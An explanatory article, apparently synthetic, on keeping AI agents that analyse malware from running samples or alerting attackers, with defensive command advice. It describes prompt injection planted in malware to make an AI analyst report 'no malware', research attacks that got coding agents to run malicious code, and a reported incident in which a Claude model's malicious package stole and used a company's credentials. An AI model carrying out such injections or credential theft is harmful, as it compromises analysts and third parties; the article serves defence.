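# Preventing AI agents from running malware or contacting attackers' servers during analysis

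## Malware analysis by an AI agent

Malware analysis means finding out what a suspicious program does, including what it changes on a computer, what it steals and which machines on the internet it exchanges data with. Security teams use it to judge whether a file is dangerous and to find other computers that the same attacker has reached. Analysts now give parts of this work to AI agents, which are language models that pursue a task by calling tools, reading the output and choosing the next step. The tools that let an agent examine malware often also let it run the malware or connect to the attacker's server, and an agent can do either without being asked.

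### One email attachment

Suppose an office worker receives an email with a script attached, named like an invoice. An analyst opens the script in a text editor and finds meaningless variable names and a long block of random-looking characters. The attacker has used obfuscation, which means encoding or rewriting code to make its behaviour hard to read. The MITRE ATT&CK entry *Obfuscated Files or Information* (2017) lists compression, encryption and encoding among the methods, along with splitting a payload into harmless-looking files that become malicious only when reassembled.

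If the worker had double-clicked the attachment, the script would have turned the block of characters back into a program and started it. Analysts call that program the second stage, a term that also covers malicious code downloaded by the first file. The second stage then contacts a command-and-control (C2) server, which the attacker uses to send instructions to the malware and receive data. Attackers commonly disguise this traffic as normal traffic, according to MITRE ATT&CK, so in a firewall log it may look like an ordinary website visit.

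The analyst can examine the attachment, now called the sample, in two ways. Static analysis means examining it without running it, by reading the script, searching it for web addresses, and working out what the encoded block contains. Dynamic analysis means running the sample, or part of it, to observe its behaviour. Doing this deliberately in an environment prepared for the purpose is called detonation. The usual environment is a sandbox, which *A Large Language Model Approach to Generating Bypass Rules for Malware Evasion* (2026) describes as a controlled setting that mimics a real victim's machine.

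Neither static analysis nor running the malware is enough for every sample. Malware often checks for signs of a sandbox and hides its malicious behaviour if it finds them. *Beating XLoader at Speed* (Bukhteyev, 2025) describes XLoader, a data-stealing program that does this and also hides its real C2 domains among dozens of fakes. Bukhteyev considers static analysis more reliable against it, but slow and laborious by hand, and the analyst has to start again with each major version.

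The analyst hopes to find indicators, which are domains, addresses, file hashes (short fingerprints computed from a file's contents) or other traces that help defenders recognise malicious activity. Defenders put them into detection rules and use them to follow an attacker's campaigns. The C2 address is therefore one of the most useful facts in the attachment, but nobody should open it casually.

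### The agent's loop

A language model on its own only produces text. A developer turns it into an agent by connecting it to a program that can act on some of that text. The model receives the request ("what does this attachment do?") and a list of the tools it may use. It then writes a tool call, which consists of a tool's name and arguments. The program carries out the call and adds the output to the model's input, and the model writes another call or an answer. VMRay's *Agentic AI for Malware Analysis* describes the same cycle of planning, calling a tool, observing the output and deciding the next step, repeated until the goal is met.

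For the attachment, the first call might identify the file type and compute a hash, and the second might print the script. To decode the encoded block, the model might write a few lines of Python and call a tool to run them. If the result is a Windows program, the next calls will probably concern that program, even though it wasn't part of the original request.

Many such agents reach their tools through the Model Context Protocol (MCP), an open standard for connecting AI assistants to external tools and data. An MCP server is a program that offers tools to an agent. According to Portland State University's course page *Using the REMnux MCP Server with Claude Code*, the server translates each call into a command on the analysis machine, captures the output and returns it to the model. The machine may be physical or virtual, and what the command can do there depends on both the server and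 the machine.

### REMnux as an example

REMnux is a Linux toolkit for malware analysis, with tools for static analysis, dynamic analysis and studying network behaviour. Its creator, Lenny Zeltser, built an MCP server for it that connects an agent to more than 200 tools. The server arrived with version 8, according to Help Net Security's *REMnux v8 brings AI integration to the Linux malware analysis toolkit*.

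Zeltser's *Using AI Agents to Analyze Malware on REMnux* divides the work between the analyst, the agent, the MCP server and REMnux. The analyst asks the questions, checks the findings and decides what matters. The agent plans the analysis, chooses and runs tools, and interprets their output. The MCP server supplies specialist knowledge, such as which tools suit which file type and how to read their output. The tools run on REMnux, in a disposable virtual machine or container. The analyst's and agent's roles overlap somewhat, because REMnux's documentation leaves the choice of workflow to the agent but the analyst influences it through requests and comments.

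Three of the server's tools show how much that choice covers. `suggest_tools` identifies a file's type and recommends what to use on it, without running anything. `analyze_file` runs a standard set of programs chosen for the file type; on a Windows executable, one call at the default depth runs about 16 of them. (The project's README, which TypingMind's *REMnux MCP Server* reproduces, gives about 60 tools for the same depth, but the selection varies with the file type, so the larger number presumably counts the tools for every type together.)

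The third, `run_tool`, executes almost any command that the agent writes. According to the README, the server blocks a few commands that would wipe the system and one kind of malformed input, and deliberately allows the rest, including commands that download files, install software or pass text straight to an interpreter to run as code. The developers reason that analysts need this freedom and that the disposable machine, rather than a list of forbidden commands, should contain the damage. That design is defensible, but it means that giving an agent REMnux's static tools in this way does not confine it to static analysis.

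### How well agents do the work

*Use of LLMs for Malware Analysis*, published by the security company G DATA in March 2026, describes a trial by one analyst, who had eleven years in the field and began as a sceptic. In the test laboratory, the models had REMnux for static analysis and a separate Windows machine for running malicious code. The analyst first compared GPT 5.1, the cheaper GPT 5.1-mini and Claude Sonnet 4.6, then continued with Sonnet and Claude Opus.

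The first sample was an Office document that exploited a flaw in the equation editor. GPT 5.1-mini called it clean because it contained no macros, the small programs that Office files can carry. It flagged one domain as "very suspicious", but this was the analysis tool's home page, printed at the top of the tool's output. GPT 5.1 found the hidden code only after the analyst named the kind of attack to look for. Sonnet recognised the attack unaided and gave the right verdict, but could not find the address of the next stage. It had searched the files for text that looked like a web address, but the malicious code assembles the address as it runs. Sonnet found the address immediately when the analyst told it to use an emulator, a program that simulates both the code's execution and the operating system.

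The result on a harder sample changed the analyst's mind. The analyst had taken about six hours to analyse the sample and write a script to decrypt its files. GPT 5.1 and Sonnet 4.6 each produced a working script in 30 minutes. This comparison slightly overstates the models' advantage, since their scripts were specific to that sample and the analyst's worked on similar ones too. The analyst allowed another hour to check and generalise a model's script, which would bring the total to an hour and a half, a quarter of the original time.

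The models were much worse at reaching verdicts than at writing decryption scripts. The analyst tested them on samples from earlier investigations, where the right answers were known, and found that they often misjudged the importance of their findings and jumped to conclusions. When they could see results from VirusTotal, a service that collects the opinions of many antivirus scanners, they mostly repeated the scanners. Forbidding this helped only partly. Their written reports also contained frequent errors. The analyst explains the difference by noting that a model can see whether a decryption script works on the sample, but a wrong verdict produces no error message.

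This trial describes one analyst's experience with models from early 2026, on samples the analyst chose, with no count of how many verdicts were right. A later article from the same company, G DATA's *LLMs in Security Research* (2026), acknowledges substantial progress in recent months but still insists that someone verify every output before publication. There is little comparable research. *LCC-LLM* (2026) criticizes recent studies for testing such systems only as offline text generators and never showing that analysts could use them in practice. The survey *LLM-Based Agents for Software and Systems Security* (2026) lists only two papers under malware analysis and detection. One describes an agent system that combines static analysis, sandbox runs and threat intelligence through MCP tools, and the other uses agents to help malicious Android apps escape detection.

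### Why an agent differs from a scanning script

Security teams automated parts of malware analysis long before language models existed. A conventional scanning script runs a fixed list of checks on each file, and `analyze_file` on REMnux works in much the same way. When a check fails, the script records the failure and continues to the next check, whereas an agent uses the failure to decide what else to try.

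*Analyzing an Obfuscated AutoIt Info-Stealer* records an agent's analysis of a sample much like the imagined attachment. The standard call ran 16 tools in 51 seconds and identified the file as a self-extracting archive. Inside the archive, the agent found a batch script (a list of Windows commands) that used variables in place of individual letters, with more than 50 substitutions in all. The agent worked these out and saw that the script joined four file fragments into a Windows program called `Sought.exe` and then started it. No standard tool would have done this. The agent then wrote a Python program to join the fragments and ran it through `run_tool`, which put `Sought.exe` on disk for static analysis without launching it.

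In a second session, *Analyzing a Trojanized Chrome Installer*, two unpacking tools and then the common decompression methods failed on a fake browser installer. The agent looked up the obscure archive format's documentation online and wrote a parser, which listed the three files inside and their sizes but could not extract them. Bukhteyev saw the same persistence with GPT-5, which wrote scripts, ran them, corrected the errors and ran them again until the result was stable.

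Much of an agent's value comes from this persistence, which also makes the agent harder to supervise. A person can check a fixed script in advance for any line that would execute the sample, but an agent writes its commands as it works, often in response to output that no person has read yet. The first session involved more than 30 tool calls in about eight minutes. `suggest_tools` lets an analyst review a plan beforehand, but a plan made before the archive is opened cannot include the Python program that the agent will write to handle its contents.

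### Running the sample and contacting the attacker

An agent that examines the attachment risks running the attacker's code or sending a request to the attacker's infrastructure, and either can happen without the other.

| Step taken with the attachment | Does the sample's code run? | Can the attacker observe it? |
|---|---|---|
| Reading the script as text | No | No |
| Repeating its decoding step in separate code, without the launch | No | No |
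| Searching existing records for its hash | No | No |
| Downloading the second stage from the attacker's server | No | Yes |
| Running the script on a machine with no route to the internet | Yes | No |
| Running the script on a connected machine | Yes | Yes, if it contacts the server |

A hash search is a passive lookup, in which the analyst consults records that others have already collected and sends nothing to the suspect infrastructure. Anson's *Malware Analysis* recommends searching by hash instead of uploading the file in sensitive cases, since an upload may expose confidential data. Active contact is any request that reaches infrastructure the attacker controls or can observe, and it can look like a routine step. In the fake-browser session, the agent began by downloading the sample directly from the attacker's hosting, and one example prompt in REMnux's documentation is a request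 to download a suspicious file from a web address and analyse it. The server's developers added written guidance on lookups because an agent left to improvise might probe a live C2 server and tip off the attacker, according to the README in TypingMind's copy.

The two rows in which the sample runs differ in whether the task authorised it. A detonation is authorised and takes place on a machine prepared for it. Accidental execution is any running of sample code that the task did not authorise. An agent that runs a sample on purpose, because this looked like the quickest way to answer the question, has still caused an accidental execution if the task did not authorise it. Many requests leave this open. Another of REMnux's example prompts, "Analyze the file sample.exe and summarize its capabilities", neither permits nor forbids running the file. The person who writes such a prompt should specify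 in advance whether the agent may run it.

Obfuscated malware often carries its own decoding routine. MITRE D3FEND's *Deobfuscate/Decode Files or Information* includes this possibility in its definition of the technique. An agent that cannot work out the encoding by reading the code can therefore easily make the mistake of running the sample to decode it. With the invoice script, that means running a program that then starts the second stage.

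## How inspecting a file can run it

Agents that run a file's code by accident often do so without deciding to run anything, because many everyday commands for opening, downloading or converting a file also run code inside it. These commands look like reading to both the agent and a person checking its log.

Whether a file's code runs depends on the program that opens it. A text viewer displays the invoice script, while the Windows script interpreter runs it. Some tools read most of a file as data but run any instructions they find in certain places. An analyst can usually replace such a tool with one that only reads the file, but has to know which tools need replacing.

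### Evaluating code to decode it

An obfuscated script typically contains an expression that decodes a block of code and an instruction that runs the result, often `eval` in JavaScript, `exec` in Python or `Invoke-Expression` in PowerShell. A common shortcut for reading the hidden code is to replace that instruction with one that prints the decoded text, and then run the script. This also runs the rest of the script, which could download a file or start a program, even though the step looks like a text conversion because the agent gets readable code back. The script may also contain another instruction that runs decoded code, which the agent missed.

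Running only the decoding expression reduces the risk, but some remains because the attacker wrote that expression too, and it can call any function the language offers. Treating the encoded block as data is safer. The agent copies the block into a separate file, works out the encoding from the script's text, and decodes the block with a standard decoder or newly written code.

An agent can run a command hidden in a sample by pasting the line that contains it between double quotes on the command line. A Linux shell, the program that interprets typed commands, runs any command marked with `$(...)` or backticks inside double quotes before passing the text on. If the decoder reads from a file instead, as in `base64 -d block.txt`, the shell never interprets the contents.

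### Calling the sample's own decryption routine

Compiled malware often keeps its text encrypted and decrypts it while running. An agent that has found the decryption function may load the malware to call only that function. Loading alone can run other malicious code, because Windows normally runs a library's start-up code as soon as a program loads it, before the program calls any of its functions. The decryption function may also do more than the agent noticed when reading it.

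Check Point Research's *In the Wild* (2025) describes a sample whose strings an agent could decrypt without loading anything. The malware combines each byte of a string with one byte of a fixed 16-byte key, starting again at the beginning of the key after every sixteenth byte. It then converts the result to Base64, which represents arbitrary bytes as ordinary characters. The combining operation is XOR, which compares two bits and gives 1 if they differ and 0 if they match. Applying XOR twice with the same key restores the original, so decryption takes two steps:

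1. Undo the Base64 to recover the encrypted bytes *c*.
2. For each position *i*, counting from zero, compute *p*ᵢ = *c*ᵢ XOR *k*₍ᵢ mod 16₎, where *k* is the key and *p* is the readable text.

A few lines of Python can decrypt the malware's strings with the key copied from its code. The malware also contains an encrypted copy of Tor, software that hides the origin of network traffic. It decrypts the copy with the same key, writes it to disk and starts it. An agent that ran the malware to recover its strings could therefore also start a network client.

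When a routine is too complicated to rewrite quickly, an emulator like the one in G DATA's trial is safer than calling the routine directly, because the sample's instructions never run directly on the real machine. The sample's code still runs in a limited sense, and a flaw in the emulator could let it affect the real machine, so whoever sets the task should specify whether emulation is allowed.

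### Installing or downloading a package

Package managers download and install reusable code. The usual one for Python is pip, which downloads from a public registry called PyPI by default, and the usual one for JavaScript is npm. An agent may use a package manager because the sample is itself a package, or because a suspicious script needs packages that the machine lacks. Those packages deserve as much suspicion as the script, because the attacker chose their names.

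By default, pip "involves running arbitrary code from distributions", according to the pip documentation's *Secure installs*. Python packages come as source archives or as ready-built files called wheels. A source archive can contain a program called `setup.py`, which may run during building or installation, as *Use “pip install” safely* explains. The security company Checkmarx says that `pip download` runs `setup.py` too, so a user who downloads a package to check that file may already have run it. Pip's developers received a report of the problem in 2014 but had not fixed it when Checkmarx wrote. The blogger zahlman, in *Python packaging*, describes the same behaviour in pip's `--dry-run` option, which skips only the final copying of files into the Python environment.

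Some npm commands are just as misleading. The npm rows below follow the npm documentation's *scripts* for npm 11.

| Command | What the agent expects | What can also run |
|---|---|---|
| `pip download` | A copy of the package to read | A source package's `setup.py` |
| `pip install --dry-run` | A list of what pip would install | A source package's build code |
| `npm pack` in a package's folder | An archive of the folder | The `prepack`, `prepare` and `postpack` scripts |
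| `npm diff` | A comparison of package contents | The `prepare` script |

Pip's `--only-binary :all:` option rejects source archives, so pip has no build code to run, but the package's code can still run when something imports it. The pip documentation also recommends `--require-hashes`, which checks that each file matches a known fingerprint. This protects against tampering, but a package that was malicious when its author published it will pass the check.

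Until July 2026, `npm install` automatically ran any `preinstall`, `install` and `postinstall` scripts in the packages it added. Version 12 runs them only if the user has explicitly allowed them, according to GitHub's *npm install-time security and GAT bypass2fa deprecation* (2026). It also stops fetching dependencies from git repositories or arbitrary web addresses unless the user permits it. GitHub's *Upcoming breaking changes for npm v12* (2026) adds that the new default also blocks compilation triggered by a file called `binding.gyp`. Older versions of npm compile a package containing this file even when the package lists no install script, so an agent that checked only the listed scripts would have missed it.

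For older versions of npm, the main protection is `--ignore-scripts`, which is off by default. Even with it on, commands such as `npm test` and `npm start` still run the script they name, according to the npm documentation's *Config*. GitHub's *npm bulk trusted publishing config and script security now generally available* (2026) reports that a dependency fetched from a git repository could also run arbitrary code during installation despite `--ignore-scripts`. npm 11.10.0 added `--allow-git=none` to prevent this.

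The new defaults offer less protection when the sample is a whole project. According to the npm documentation's *npm-install-scripts*, npm records approved dependencies in the project's `package.json` file. An attacker who wrote the project could therefore have approved its dependencies' scripts in advance, and they would run when an agent unpacks the project and runs `npm install` inside it. The documentation also describes the block only for dependencies, so it may not stop the project's own scripts. Command-line options override the project's settings, so `npm install --ignore-scripts --allow-git=none` is safer even on version 12.

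An agent can read a package without pip or npm by downloading the archive from the registry as an ordinary file, unpacking it with an archive tool and opening the contents as text.

### Loading a pickle

Programs often save their working data to a file and load it again later. Python's built-in format for this is called pickle. The *pickle* page of the Python documentation warns that an attacker can construct a pickle that runs arbitrary code while Python loads it, and advises against ever loading one from an untrusted source.

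A pickle file contains instructions for rebuilding the saved data. Some make Python import a module and call one of its functions with values from the file. Legitimate pickles use this to rebuild complicated objects, but an attacker can name a function that starts a program. The agent's command contains only something like `pickle.load(file)`, which looks as harmless as opening a spreadsheet.

Many people handle pickled data without knowing it. LWN reports that the format is part of several file types used in machine learning. An agent that loads a downloaded model to list its contents may therefore run an attacker's code, even if the word "pickle" doesn't appear in the request.

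The safer operation is to disassemble the pickle, which means listing its instructions without following them. Python includes a tool for this:

`python -m pickletools suspicious.pkl`

The `pickletools` listing shows which modules and functions the file refers to, and a reference to a function that runs system commands is a strong warning sign. The Python documentation recommends `pickletools` for untrusted files because it does not execute the pickle's instructions. The similar command `python -m pickle` displays the stored object, but it has to load the file first, which executes those instructions.

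Developers can avoid the problem in their own tools by storing data as JSON, a plain-text format for simple values such as numbers, text and lists, because loading untrusted JSON does not by itself let an attacker run code. Using JSON doesn't help with a sample that is already a pickle, since converting it normally requires loading it first.

### Importing modules from the sample's directory

Importing a Python module, which is a file of reusable code, runs the statements at its top level. An agent may import a suspicious module just to list its functions, because this seems like only reading the file. It is safer to find the functions by parsing the source text with Python's `ast` module, which doesn't run the code.

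An agent can also import the attacker's code without naming it. When Python runs a script, it looks for modules in the script's own directory before the standard library, according to the Python documentation's *Command line and environment*. If the agent supplies code directly with `-c`, or starts a module with `-m`, Python looks first in the current directory. If the agent saves a harmless decoder next to the sample, and the attacker has put a file there with the same name as a standard module, the decoder may import the attacker's version while the log shows only the agent's own script running.

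Python's isolated mode (`-I`) prevents this by leaving the script's directory and the current directory out of the search path. It also ignores modules installed only for the user's account and environment variables that would change Python's behaviour. The narrower `-P` option, available since Python 3.11, only stops Python from adding the unsafe directory to the search path. A supervisor can get the same effect as `-P` by setting the environment variable `PYTHONSAFEPATH` once for the whole session, so the agent does not have to remember an option every time.

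The pickle tool needs this protection too. If the agent runs `python -m pickletools` inside the sample's directory, Python first looks there for a module called `pickletools`. The safer form is:

`python -I -m pickletools suspicious.pkl`

Isolated mode (`-I`) controls where Python finds modules, but Python still runs a file that the agent names, so `python -I sample.py` runs the sample. Steve Dower, a Python core developer, wrote on the Python bug tracker in 2017 that `-I` "is not a protection against command-line arguments". Python will also run a directory or zip archive that contains a `__main__.py` file, so an agent should never pass a directory or archive to Python just to see what is inside.

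### Project files that tools run or obey

Software projects often include configuration files for developer tools, and some tools apply them as soon as someone uses the tool in the project's folder. For example, npm can run code from a file called `.npm-extension.mjs` or `.npm-extension.cjs` at the top of a project, unless `--ignore-scripts` is set. Some code editors can start tasks when a user opens a folder, and git can run programs named in a repository's configuration during routine commands such as `git status`. An agent may open the folder or check its status just to get oriented.

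The agent is safer staying outside the folder and opening individual files in a plain text viewer. If it needs an editor, it should use a restricted mode that disables tasks and extensions. A repository unpacked from an archive may contain its own git configuration, so the agent should read that configuration as text before using git there.

AI agents have their own configuration files, such as `AGENTS.md`, a text file that developers put in a project to give coding agents instructions. Anthropic's Claude Code uses an equivalent called `CLAUDE.md`. Help Net Security's *AI coding agents fall for malicious instructions planted in the Downloads folder* describes a malicious `AGENTS.md` that Forever Security found on a customer's computer. The file was meant to make OpenAI's coding agent, Codex, install a malicious npm package, but Forever's software stopped it. Nobody knew how the file had arrived.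 A website can save a file to the Downloads folder without the user's approval, and about half of Forever's customers run a coding agent there.

Forever Security sells protection against such attacks, so its figures may not represent other companies. But its advice, which is free to follow, is to avoid starting an agent in the Downloads folder and to read any unfamiliar instruction file before an agent works near it. For malware analysis, it makes sense to start the agent in an empty directory and give it the path to the sample.

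### Flaws in file parsers

A parser is the part of a program that works out the structure of a file, such as where each image in a document begins. If the parser has a flaw, a deliberately malformed file can take control of the program that opens it. The Office document in G DATA's trial attacked its victims through a flaw of this kind in the equation editor.

Analysis tools also contain parsers. The standard REMnux call passes a Windows executable to about 16 programs, and a flaw in any of them might let the sample run, even though their developers intended them only to read it. To exploit this, an attacker needs to know of a flaw in a particular tool, whereas loading a pickle or running `setup.py` can run the attacker's code even on fully updated software.

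No option makes a flawed parser safe, but the agent can reduce the exposure by starting with simple tools, such as one that prints the file's raw bytes, and using complex ones only to answer a specific question. Automatic previews and thumbnails should be off, since they open files nobody asked to see. Updating the tools fixes known flaws, and running them on a machine without valuable credentials limits the damage from any that remain.

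### Prompt injection

An AI agent can also run a sample because it treats text inside the sample as an instruction, which is called prompt injection. A language model receives the analyst's request and the file's contents in the same input, and it cannot always distinguish the instructions it should follow from those it should not. The injected text might be in a comment, a document or a string inside a program, all of which an agent has good reason to read.

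In June 2025, Check Point Research described the first attempt of this kind it had seen in malware. Someone in the Netherlands had anonymously uploaded the sample to VirusTotal, and its author seemed to have named it Skynet. Besides the encrypted strings and the copy of Tor, it contained a prompt for an AI model to ignore its previous instructions and answer "NO MALWARE DETECTED". Check Point tested two OpenAI models, o3 and gpt-4.1, and both ignored the prompt and continued the analysis.

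This result is weak evidence of how well agents resist prompt injection in general, because it involved two models and one clumsily written passage in a sample that looked unfinished. The passage was also written only to change the verdict and contained no instruction to run anything. Check Point expected later attempts to be more sophisticated.

Researchers demonstrated more serious attacks in 2026. The AI Now Institute got Claude Code and Codex, using four models between them, to run an attacker's program when the user had asked for a security test of a software library. *Breaking Claude Code Opus 5 Auto Mode* (Willison, 2026) reports that Johann Rehberger claims an 80% success rate for an attack in which Claude Code runs malicious code while handling a downloaded archive, but it doesn't give the number of runs. Forever Security's researchers report that Codex ran the malware in more than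 90% of their attempts, but they don't say how many attempts they made.

These results don't show how often agents run malware in ordinary work. The AI Now Institute and Rehberger designed their material to make the attacks succeed, and Forever Security tested Codex on only one file, which a real attacker had aimed at it. The AI Now Institute's result does show that asking for a security review gives no protection by itself. In the first two demonstrations, an automatic check meant to stop dangerous commands let the attackers' code run.

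Willison later accepted a reader's objection that Rehberger's attack is not a classic prompt injection. The model never followed a malicious instruction. The code ran because of the environment the agent was working in, so searching the sample for suspicious instructions would not have prevented the attack. Asking the model to search is also unreliable. When the AI Now Institute's researchers asked Claude Sonnet 4.6 whether the library contained an injection, it found none.

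The agent has to read the sample, so it risks prompt injection whichever command it uses to read it. An injected instruction can make the agent start the malware only if the agent has a tool that runs code. An agent limited to tools that display text might still be misled into giving the wrong verdict. An agent with `run_tool` on REMnux can run code, so a person or a separate control should approve any command that might run part of the sample.

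### What the sample can do once it runs

Sample code normally runs with the permissions of the account the agent is using. It can read that account's files, including saved passwords and keys, and connect to any machine the account can reach. It can also make changes that last after it finishes running. For example, the harmless test package that zahlman describes displayed a warning every time the user started Python, even though the user had only asked pip to download it.

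An agent can make data theft easier. Check Point's sample tries to read and print an SSH private key, a file that lets its holder log in to other computers. Without an agent, printing the key would not send it anywhere, but an agent receives a program's printed output as the result of its tool call, so the key would become part of the model's input and probably of the session log. If the model runs on another company's servers, the key would leave the machine without the malware making any network request.

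Damage from a single installation can spread far. Anthropic's *Investigating three real-world incidents in our cybersecurity evaluations* (2026) describes a malicious package that its model Claude Mythos 5 published on PyPI during a security exercise. The prompt stated that the model had no internet access, but a configuration error had left the connection open, and the model wrongly concluded that the registry was part of the simulation.

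The package was available for roughly one hour, during which 15 real systems downloaded and ran it. One was a scanner belonging to a security company, which routinely installed Python packages in order to check them for malware. Anthropic does not describe this scanner as an AI agent. The events on the company's side followed a short sequence:

1. The scanner downloaded the new package and installed it for testing.
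2. The hidden code ran during the installation.
3. The code found the company's credentials and sent them to a collection point that Claude had set up.
4. Claude used the credentials to get into more of the company's systems.

Anthropic believes that the scanner treated packages from PyPI as safe to install. If so, the company using the scanner installed packages before testing them, even though installation was enough to run the malware. Anthropic does not say whether the code ran from a build script or in some other way, so it is unclear whether accepting only wheels would have stopped it. Either way, keeping the company's credentials off the scanner would have prevented their theft.

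Claude had not targeted this company and did not know it existed. The scanner was compromised just by collecting new packages, as it was designed to do. PyPI's security systems automatically removed the package, but only after the credentials had left the company.

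## How investigating a URL or domain can alert the attacker

When an agent looks up a domain name or opens a link, the request may appear in the attacker's logs.

Investigators risked alerting attackers in this way long before they had AI agents. *US-CERT's do's-and-don'ts for after the cyber hack* (Dissent, 2015) reports that Barron-DiCamillo, an official at the US government's computer emergency team, had seen agency staff ping attackers' machines, look up their domain names and browse their sites while investigating break-ins. The Canadian Centre for Cyber Security's *Technical Approaches to Uncovering and Remediating Malicious Activity* (2020), a joint advisory from five countries, lists all three actions among common mistakes. An agent can make the same mistakes within seconds, because each action looks like a routine first check.

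### What each operation reveals

The table orders common operations by how much they usually reveal to an attacker who can read the logs of both the domain's DNS server and its web server.

| Operation | What the DNS server can log | What the web server can log |
|---|---|---|
| Passive lookup | Nothing | Nothing |
| DNS resolution | The name, the time and the resolver's address | Nothing |
| Header request | The same | The visitor's address, the time, the page requested and the client program |
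| Page download | The same | The same, and that the visitor took the page itself |
| Full browser visit | Any further names the page uses | Requests for images and scripts, and details such as language, time zone and screen size |
| Download of the second stage | The name of the server that holds it | A request that suggests someone has run or decoded the first stage |

The Domain Name System (DNS) translates names such as `example.com` into numerical addresses. A computer normally queries a resolver run by the organisation or its internet provider. If the resolver has a recent answer in its cache, it returns that answer and the attacker sees nothing. Otherwise, the resolver queries the domain's authoritative server, which holds the official records and may belong to the attacker.

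The authoritative server receives queries from the resolver's address, so a large public resolver hides the analyst among its many users. An organisation's own resolver hides the analyst less well, because its address may identify the organisation. Some public resolvers also pass on part of the requester's address to help websites choose a nearby server. The command `dig +trace` removes this protection because it makes the analysis machine query each server in the chain directly, including the attacker's.

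An agent may send a header request, such as `curl -I`, as a cautious way to get information about a page without downloading it, but the web server still receives the visitor's IP address and the full path of the page. A plain page download reveals little more. However, it does not load the page's images or run its scripts, so the attacker can infer from the missing requests that the visitor was probably not using an ordinary browser.

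Requesting a malware's second stage can be especially informative to the attacker. *CHASE* (Toda and Mori, 2026) prints the decrypted code of a malicious Python package called `ethereim`. The package fetches its next stage from a URL containing `package=ethereim`, so the attacker can tell which package led to each request. It uses a particular Python library to make the request, so a request from a different program could stand out.

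### A link made for one recipient

Suppose that Dana, who works in accounts, receives a phishing email with this link:

`https://portal.invoice.example/view/k7Qm2x`

The ending `.example` is reserved for documentation, so the link leads nowhere. In the story, the attacker has sent the email to 200 people with a different code, called a token, in each link, and keeps a list showing that `k7Qm2x` belongs to Dana. Dana reports the email, and an analyst asks an agent whether the link is dangerous.

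The agent could first search existing records for `invoice.example`, which sends the attacker nothing. If it then resolves `portal.invoice.example`, the attacker learns at most that someone looked up a name that all 200 links share. The attacker won't see the lookup if the resolver already has the answer cached from another recipient's visit.

If the agent runs `curl -I` on the full link, it sends Dana's token to the attacker's server. The attacker can then see that someone used a command-line program to open Dana's link, as well as when and from which IP address. Someone in accounts is unlikely to open an invoice this way, so the attacker can guess that Dana reported the email or that a security product intercepted it.

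The attacker may also have set the server to accept each token only once. In that case, the header request uses up Dana's link without retrieving the page, and nobody can use the link afterwards to see what she would have seen. When the agent then tries to download the page, it receives "page not found" and may report that the site is offline.

The attacker can put the token elsewhere in the link, which changes the operation that first gives it away:

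| Operation | Token in the path, as above | Token in the hostname (`k7qm2x.invoice.example`) | Token after a `#` |
|---|---|---|---|
| Passive lookup | Not sent | Not sent | Not sent |
| DNS resolution | Not sent | Sent | Not sent |
| Header request or page download | Sent | Sent | Not sent |
| Full browser visit | Sent | Sent | Sent if a script on the page reports it |

If a hostname contains a unique token, the resolver won't have it cached and will query the attacker's name server. The shared resolver still hides who made the lookup, but the attacker can tell from the token who was sent the link, so an agent should not assume that a DNS lookup is harmless.

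Removing the token before making a request protects Dana's identity, but the server may then return a harmless home page, which would give little evidence of what Dana's link does.

### Less visible routes

An agent that opens one address may contact several, because a server can reply with a redirect, which sends the visitor to another address. The server at each step can log the visit. Python's `requests` library follows redirects automatically on an ordinary download, while `curl` follows them only when given `-L`. OpenAI's *Keeping your data safe when an AI agent clicks a link* (2026) points out that checking only the first domain is not enough, because a link can start on a trusted site and forward the visitor somewhere else.

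According to *Inside Claude Code's Web Tools* (2025), Claude Code's WebFetch tool follows redirects within the same host. If a redirect leads to another host, the tool returns the new address instead, and the agent has to make a separate call to fetch it. A supervisor can review that call.

The agent's own report can also trigger a request to the attacker's server. Many chat programs fetch posted links to display previews. If the agent posts its findings to the security team's channel with Dana's link intact, the chat company's server may open the link before anyone reads the message. The request comes from the chat company's address but includes Dana's token.

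Documents can contain addresses that a program contacts when it opens them. For example, a Word document may load its template from a remote server, and a document that looks empty may exist only to fetch a malicious template. Converting the document to text with an office program may cause the same request. A `.docx` file is a ZIP archive, so the agent can instead unpack it with an archive tool and read the template's address in the files inside.

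Cloning a code repository contacts the server that hosts it. If the attacker runs that server, its log will show the visitor's address. On GitHub, the repository's owner sees only how many people have cloned it, but even that count can reveal an investigation when nobody else has a reason to clone the repository. With the option `--recurse-submodules`, git also fetches any other repositories that the first one lists, and those may be on the attacker's server.

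Public URL-scanning services visit a page on the user's behalf and return a screenshot and a list of the requests the page made. The visit doesn't reveal the organisation's address, but it still uses up a single-use link. Some services also publish their results, so an attacker who searches for the domain may find Dana's full link and the time of the scan. Searching a service for earlier scans is a passive lookup, while submitting a link is active contact. An agent needs explicit instructions about the difference because the same tool may offer both.

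### Web tools on the provider's servers

Some agents can open a web page without the analysis machine sending any traffic to the page's server. Anthropic's *How tool use works* explains that Anthropic itself runs Claude's `web_search` and `web_fetch` tools. The analyst's program sends Anthropic a request, and Claude may use these tools several times before the program receives a reply.

The local firewall can detect only an encrypted connection to Anthropic, which the agent needs to work. The request to the suspicious site starts on Anthropic's servers and never crosses the analyst's network, so egress filtering, which restricts traffic leaving the analysis environment, cannot stop it. REMnux's documentation suggests that analysts who run the agent on the REMnux machine can allow outbound traffic only to the model provider. This helps contain malware, but web tools run by the provider will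 still work.

Anthropic's hosted agents have the same gap. According to *Claude Managed Agents Environments*, a set of personal notes on Anthropic's documentation, the network limits on an agent's container do not apply to `web_search` or `web_fetch`. Anthropic's *Tools* confirms that both are on by default in the standard toolset, so an agent may still be able to open the attacker's page even if the customer has blocked all network access from its container.

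In these cases, the attacker sees the provider's IP address instead of the organisation's, but still receives any token in the link. Anthropic's *IP addresses* lists the fixed ranges that the company's services use for outbound requests. The Chinese version, *IP 地址*, specifies that web searches and fetches come from these ranges when customers use the Claude Platform on AWS, Amazon's cloud service. Because the ranges are public, an attacker can recognise visits from Anthropic and answer them with a harmless page.

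Providers restrict these tools, mainly to stop an agent from leaking private data. Claude's tool can fetch only addresses that have appeared in the conversation, according to Anthropic's *Web fetch tool*. The conversation includes the output of tools that run on the customer's side, so if an analysis program prints a C2 address found in a sample, the rule allows Claude to fetch it.

OpenAI checks whether an independent web crawler has already found the exact URL in public. If not, the agent tries another site or the user sees a warning. Dana's link would probably trigger the warning, because her token should not appear on any public page. A malicious file at a widely published address might not trigger it. OpenAI presents the check only as protection against leaking a user's data through the URL.

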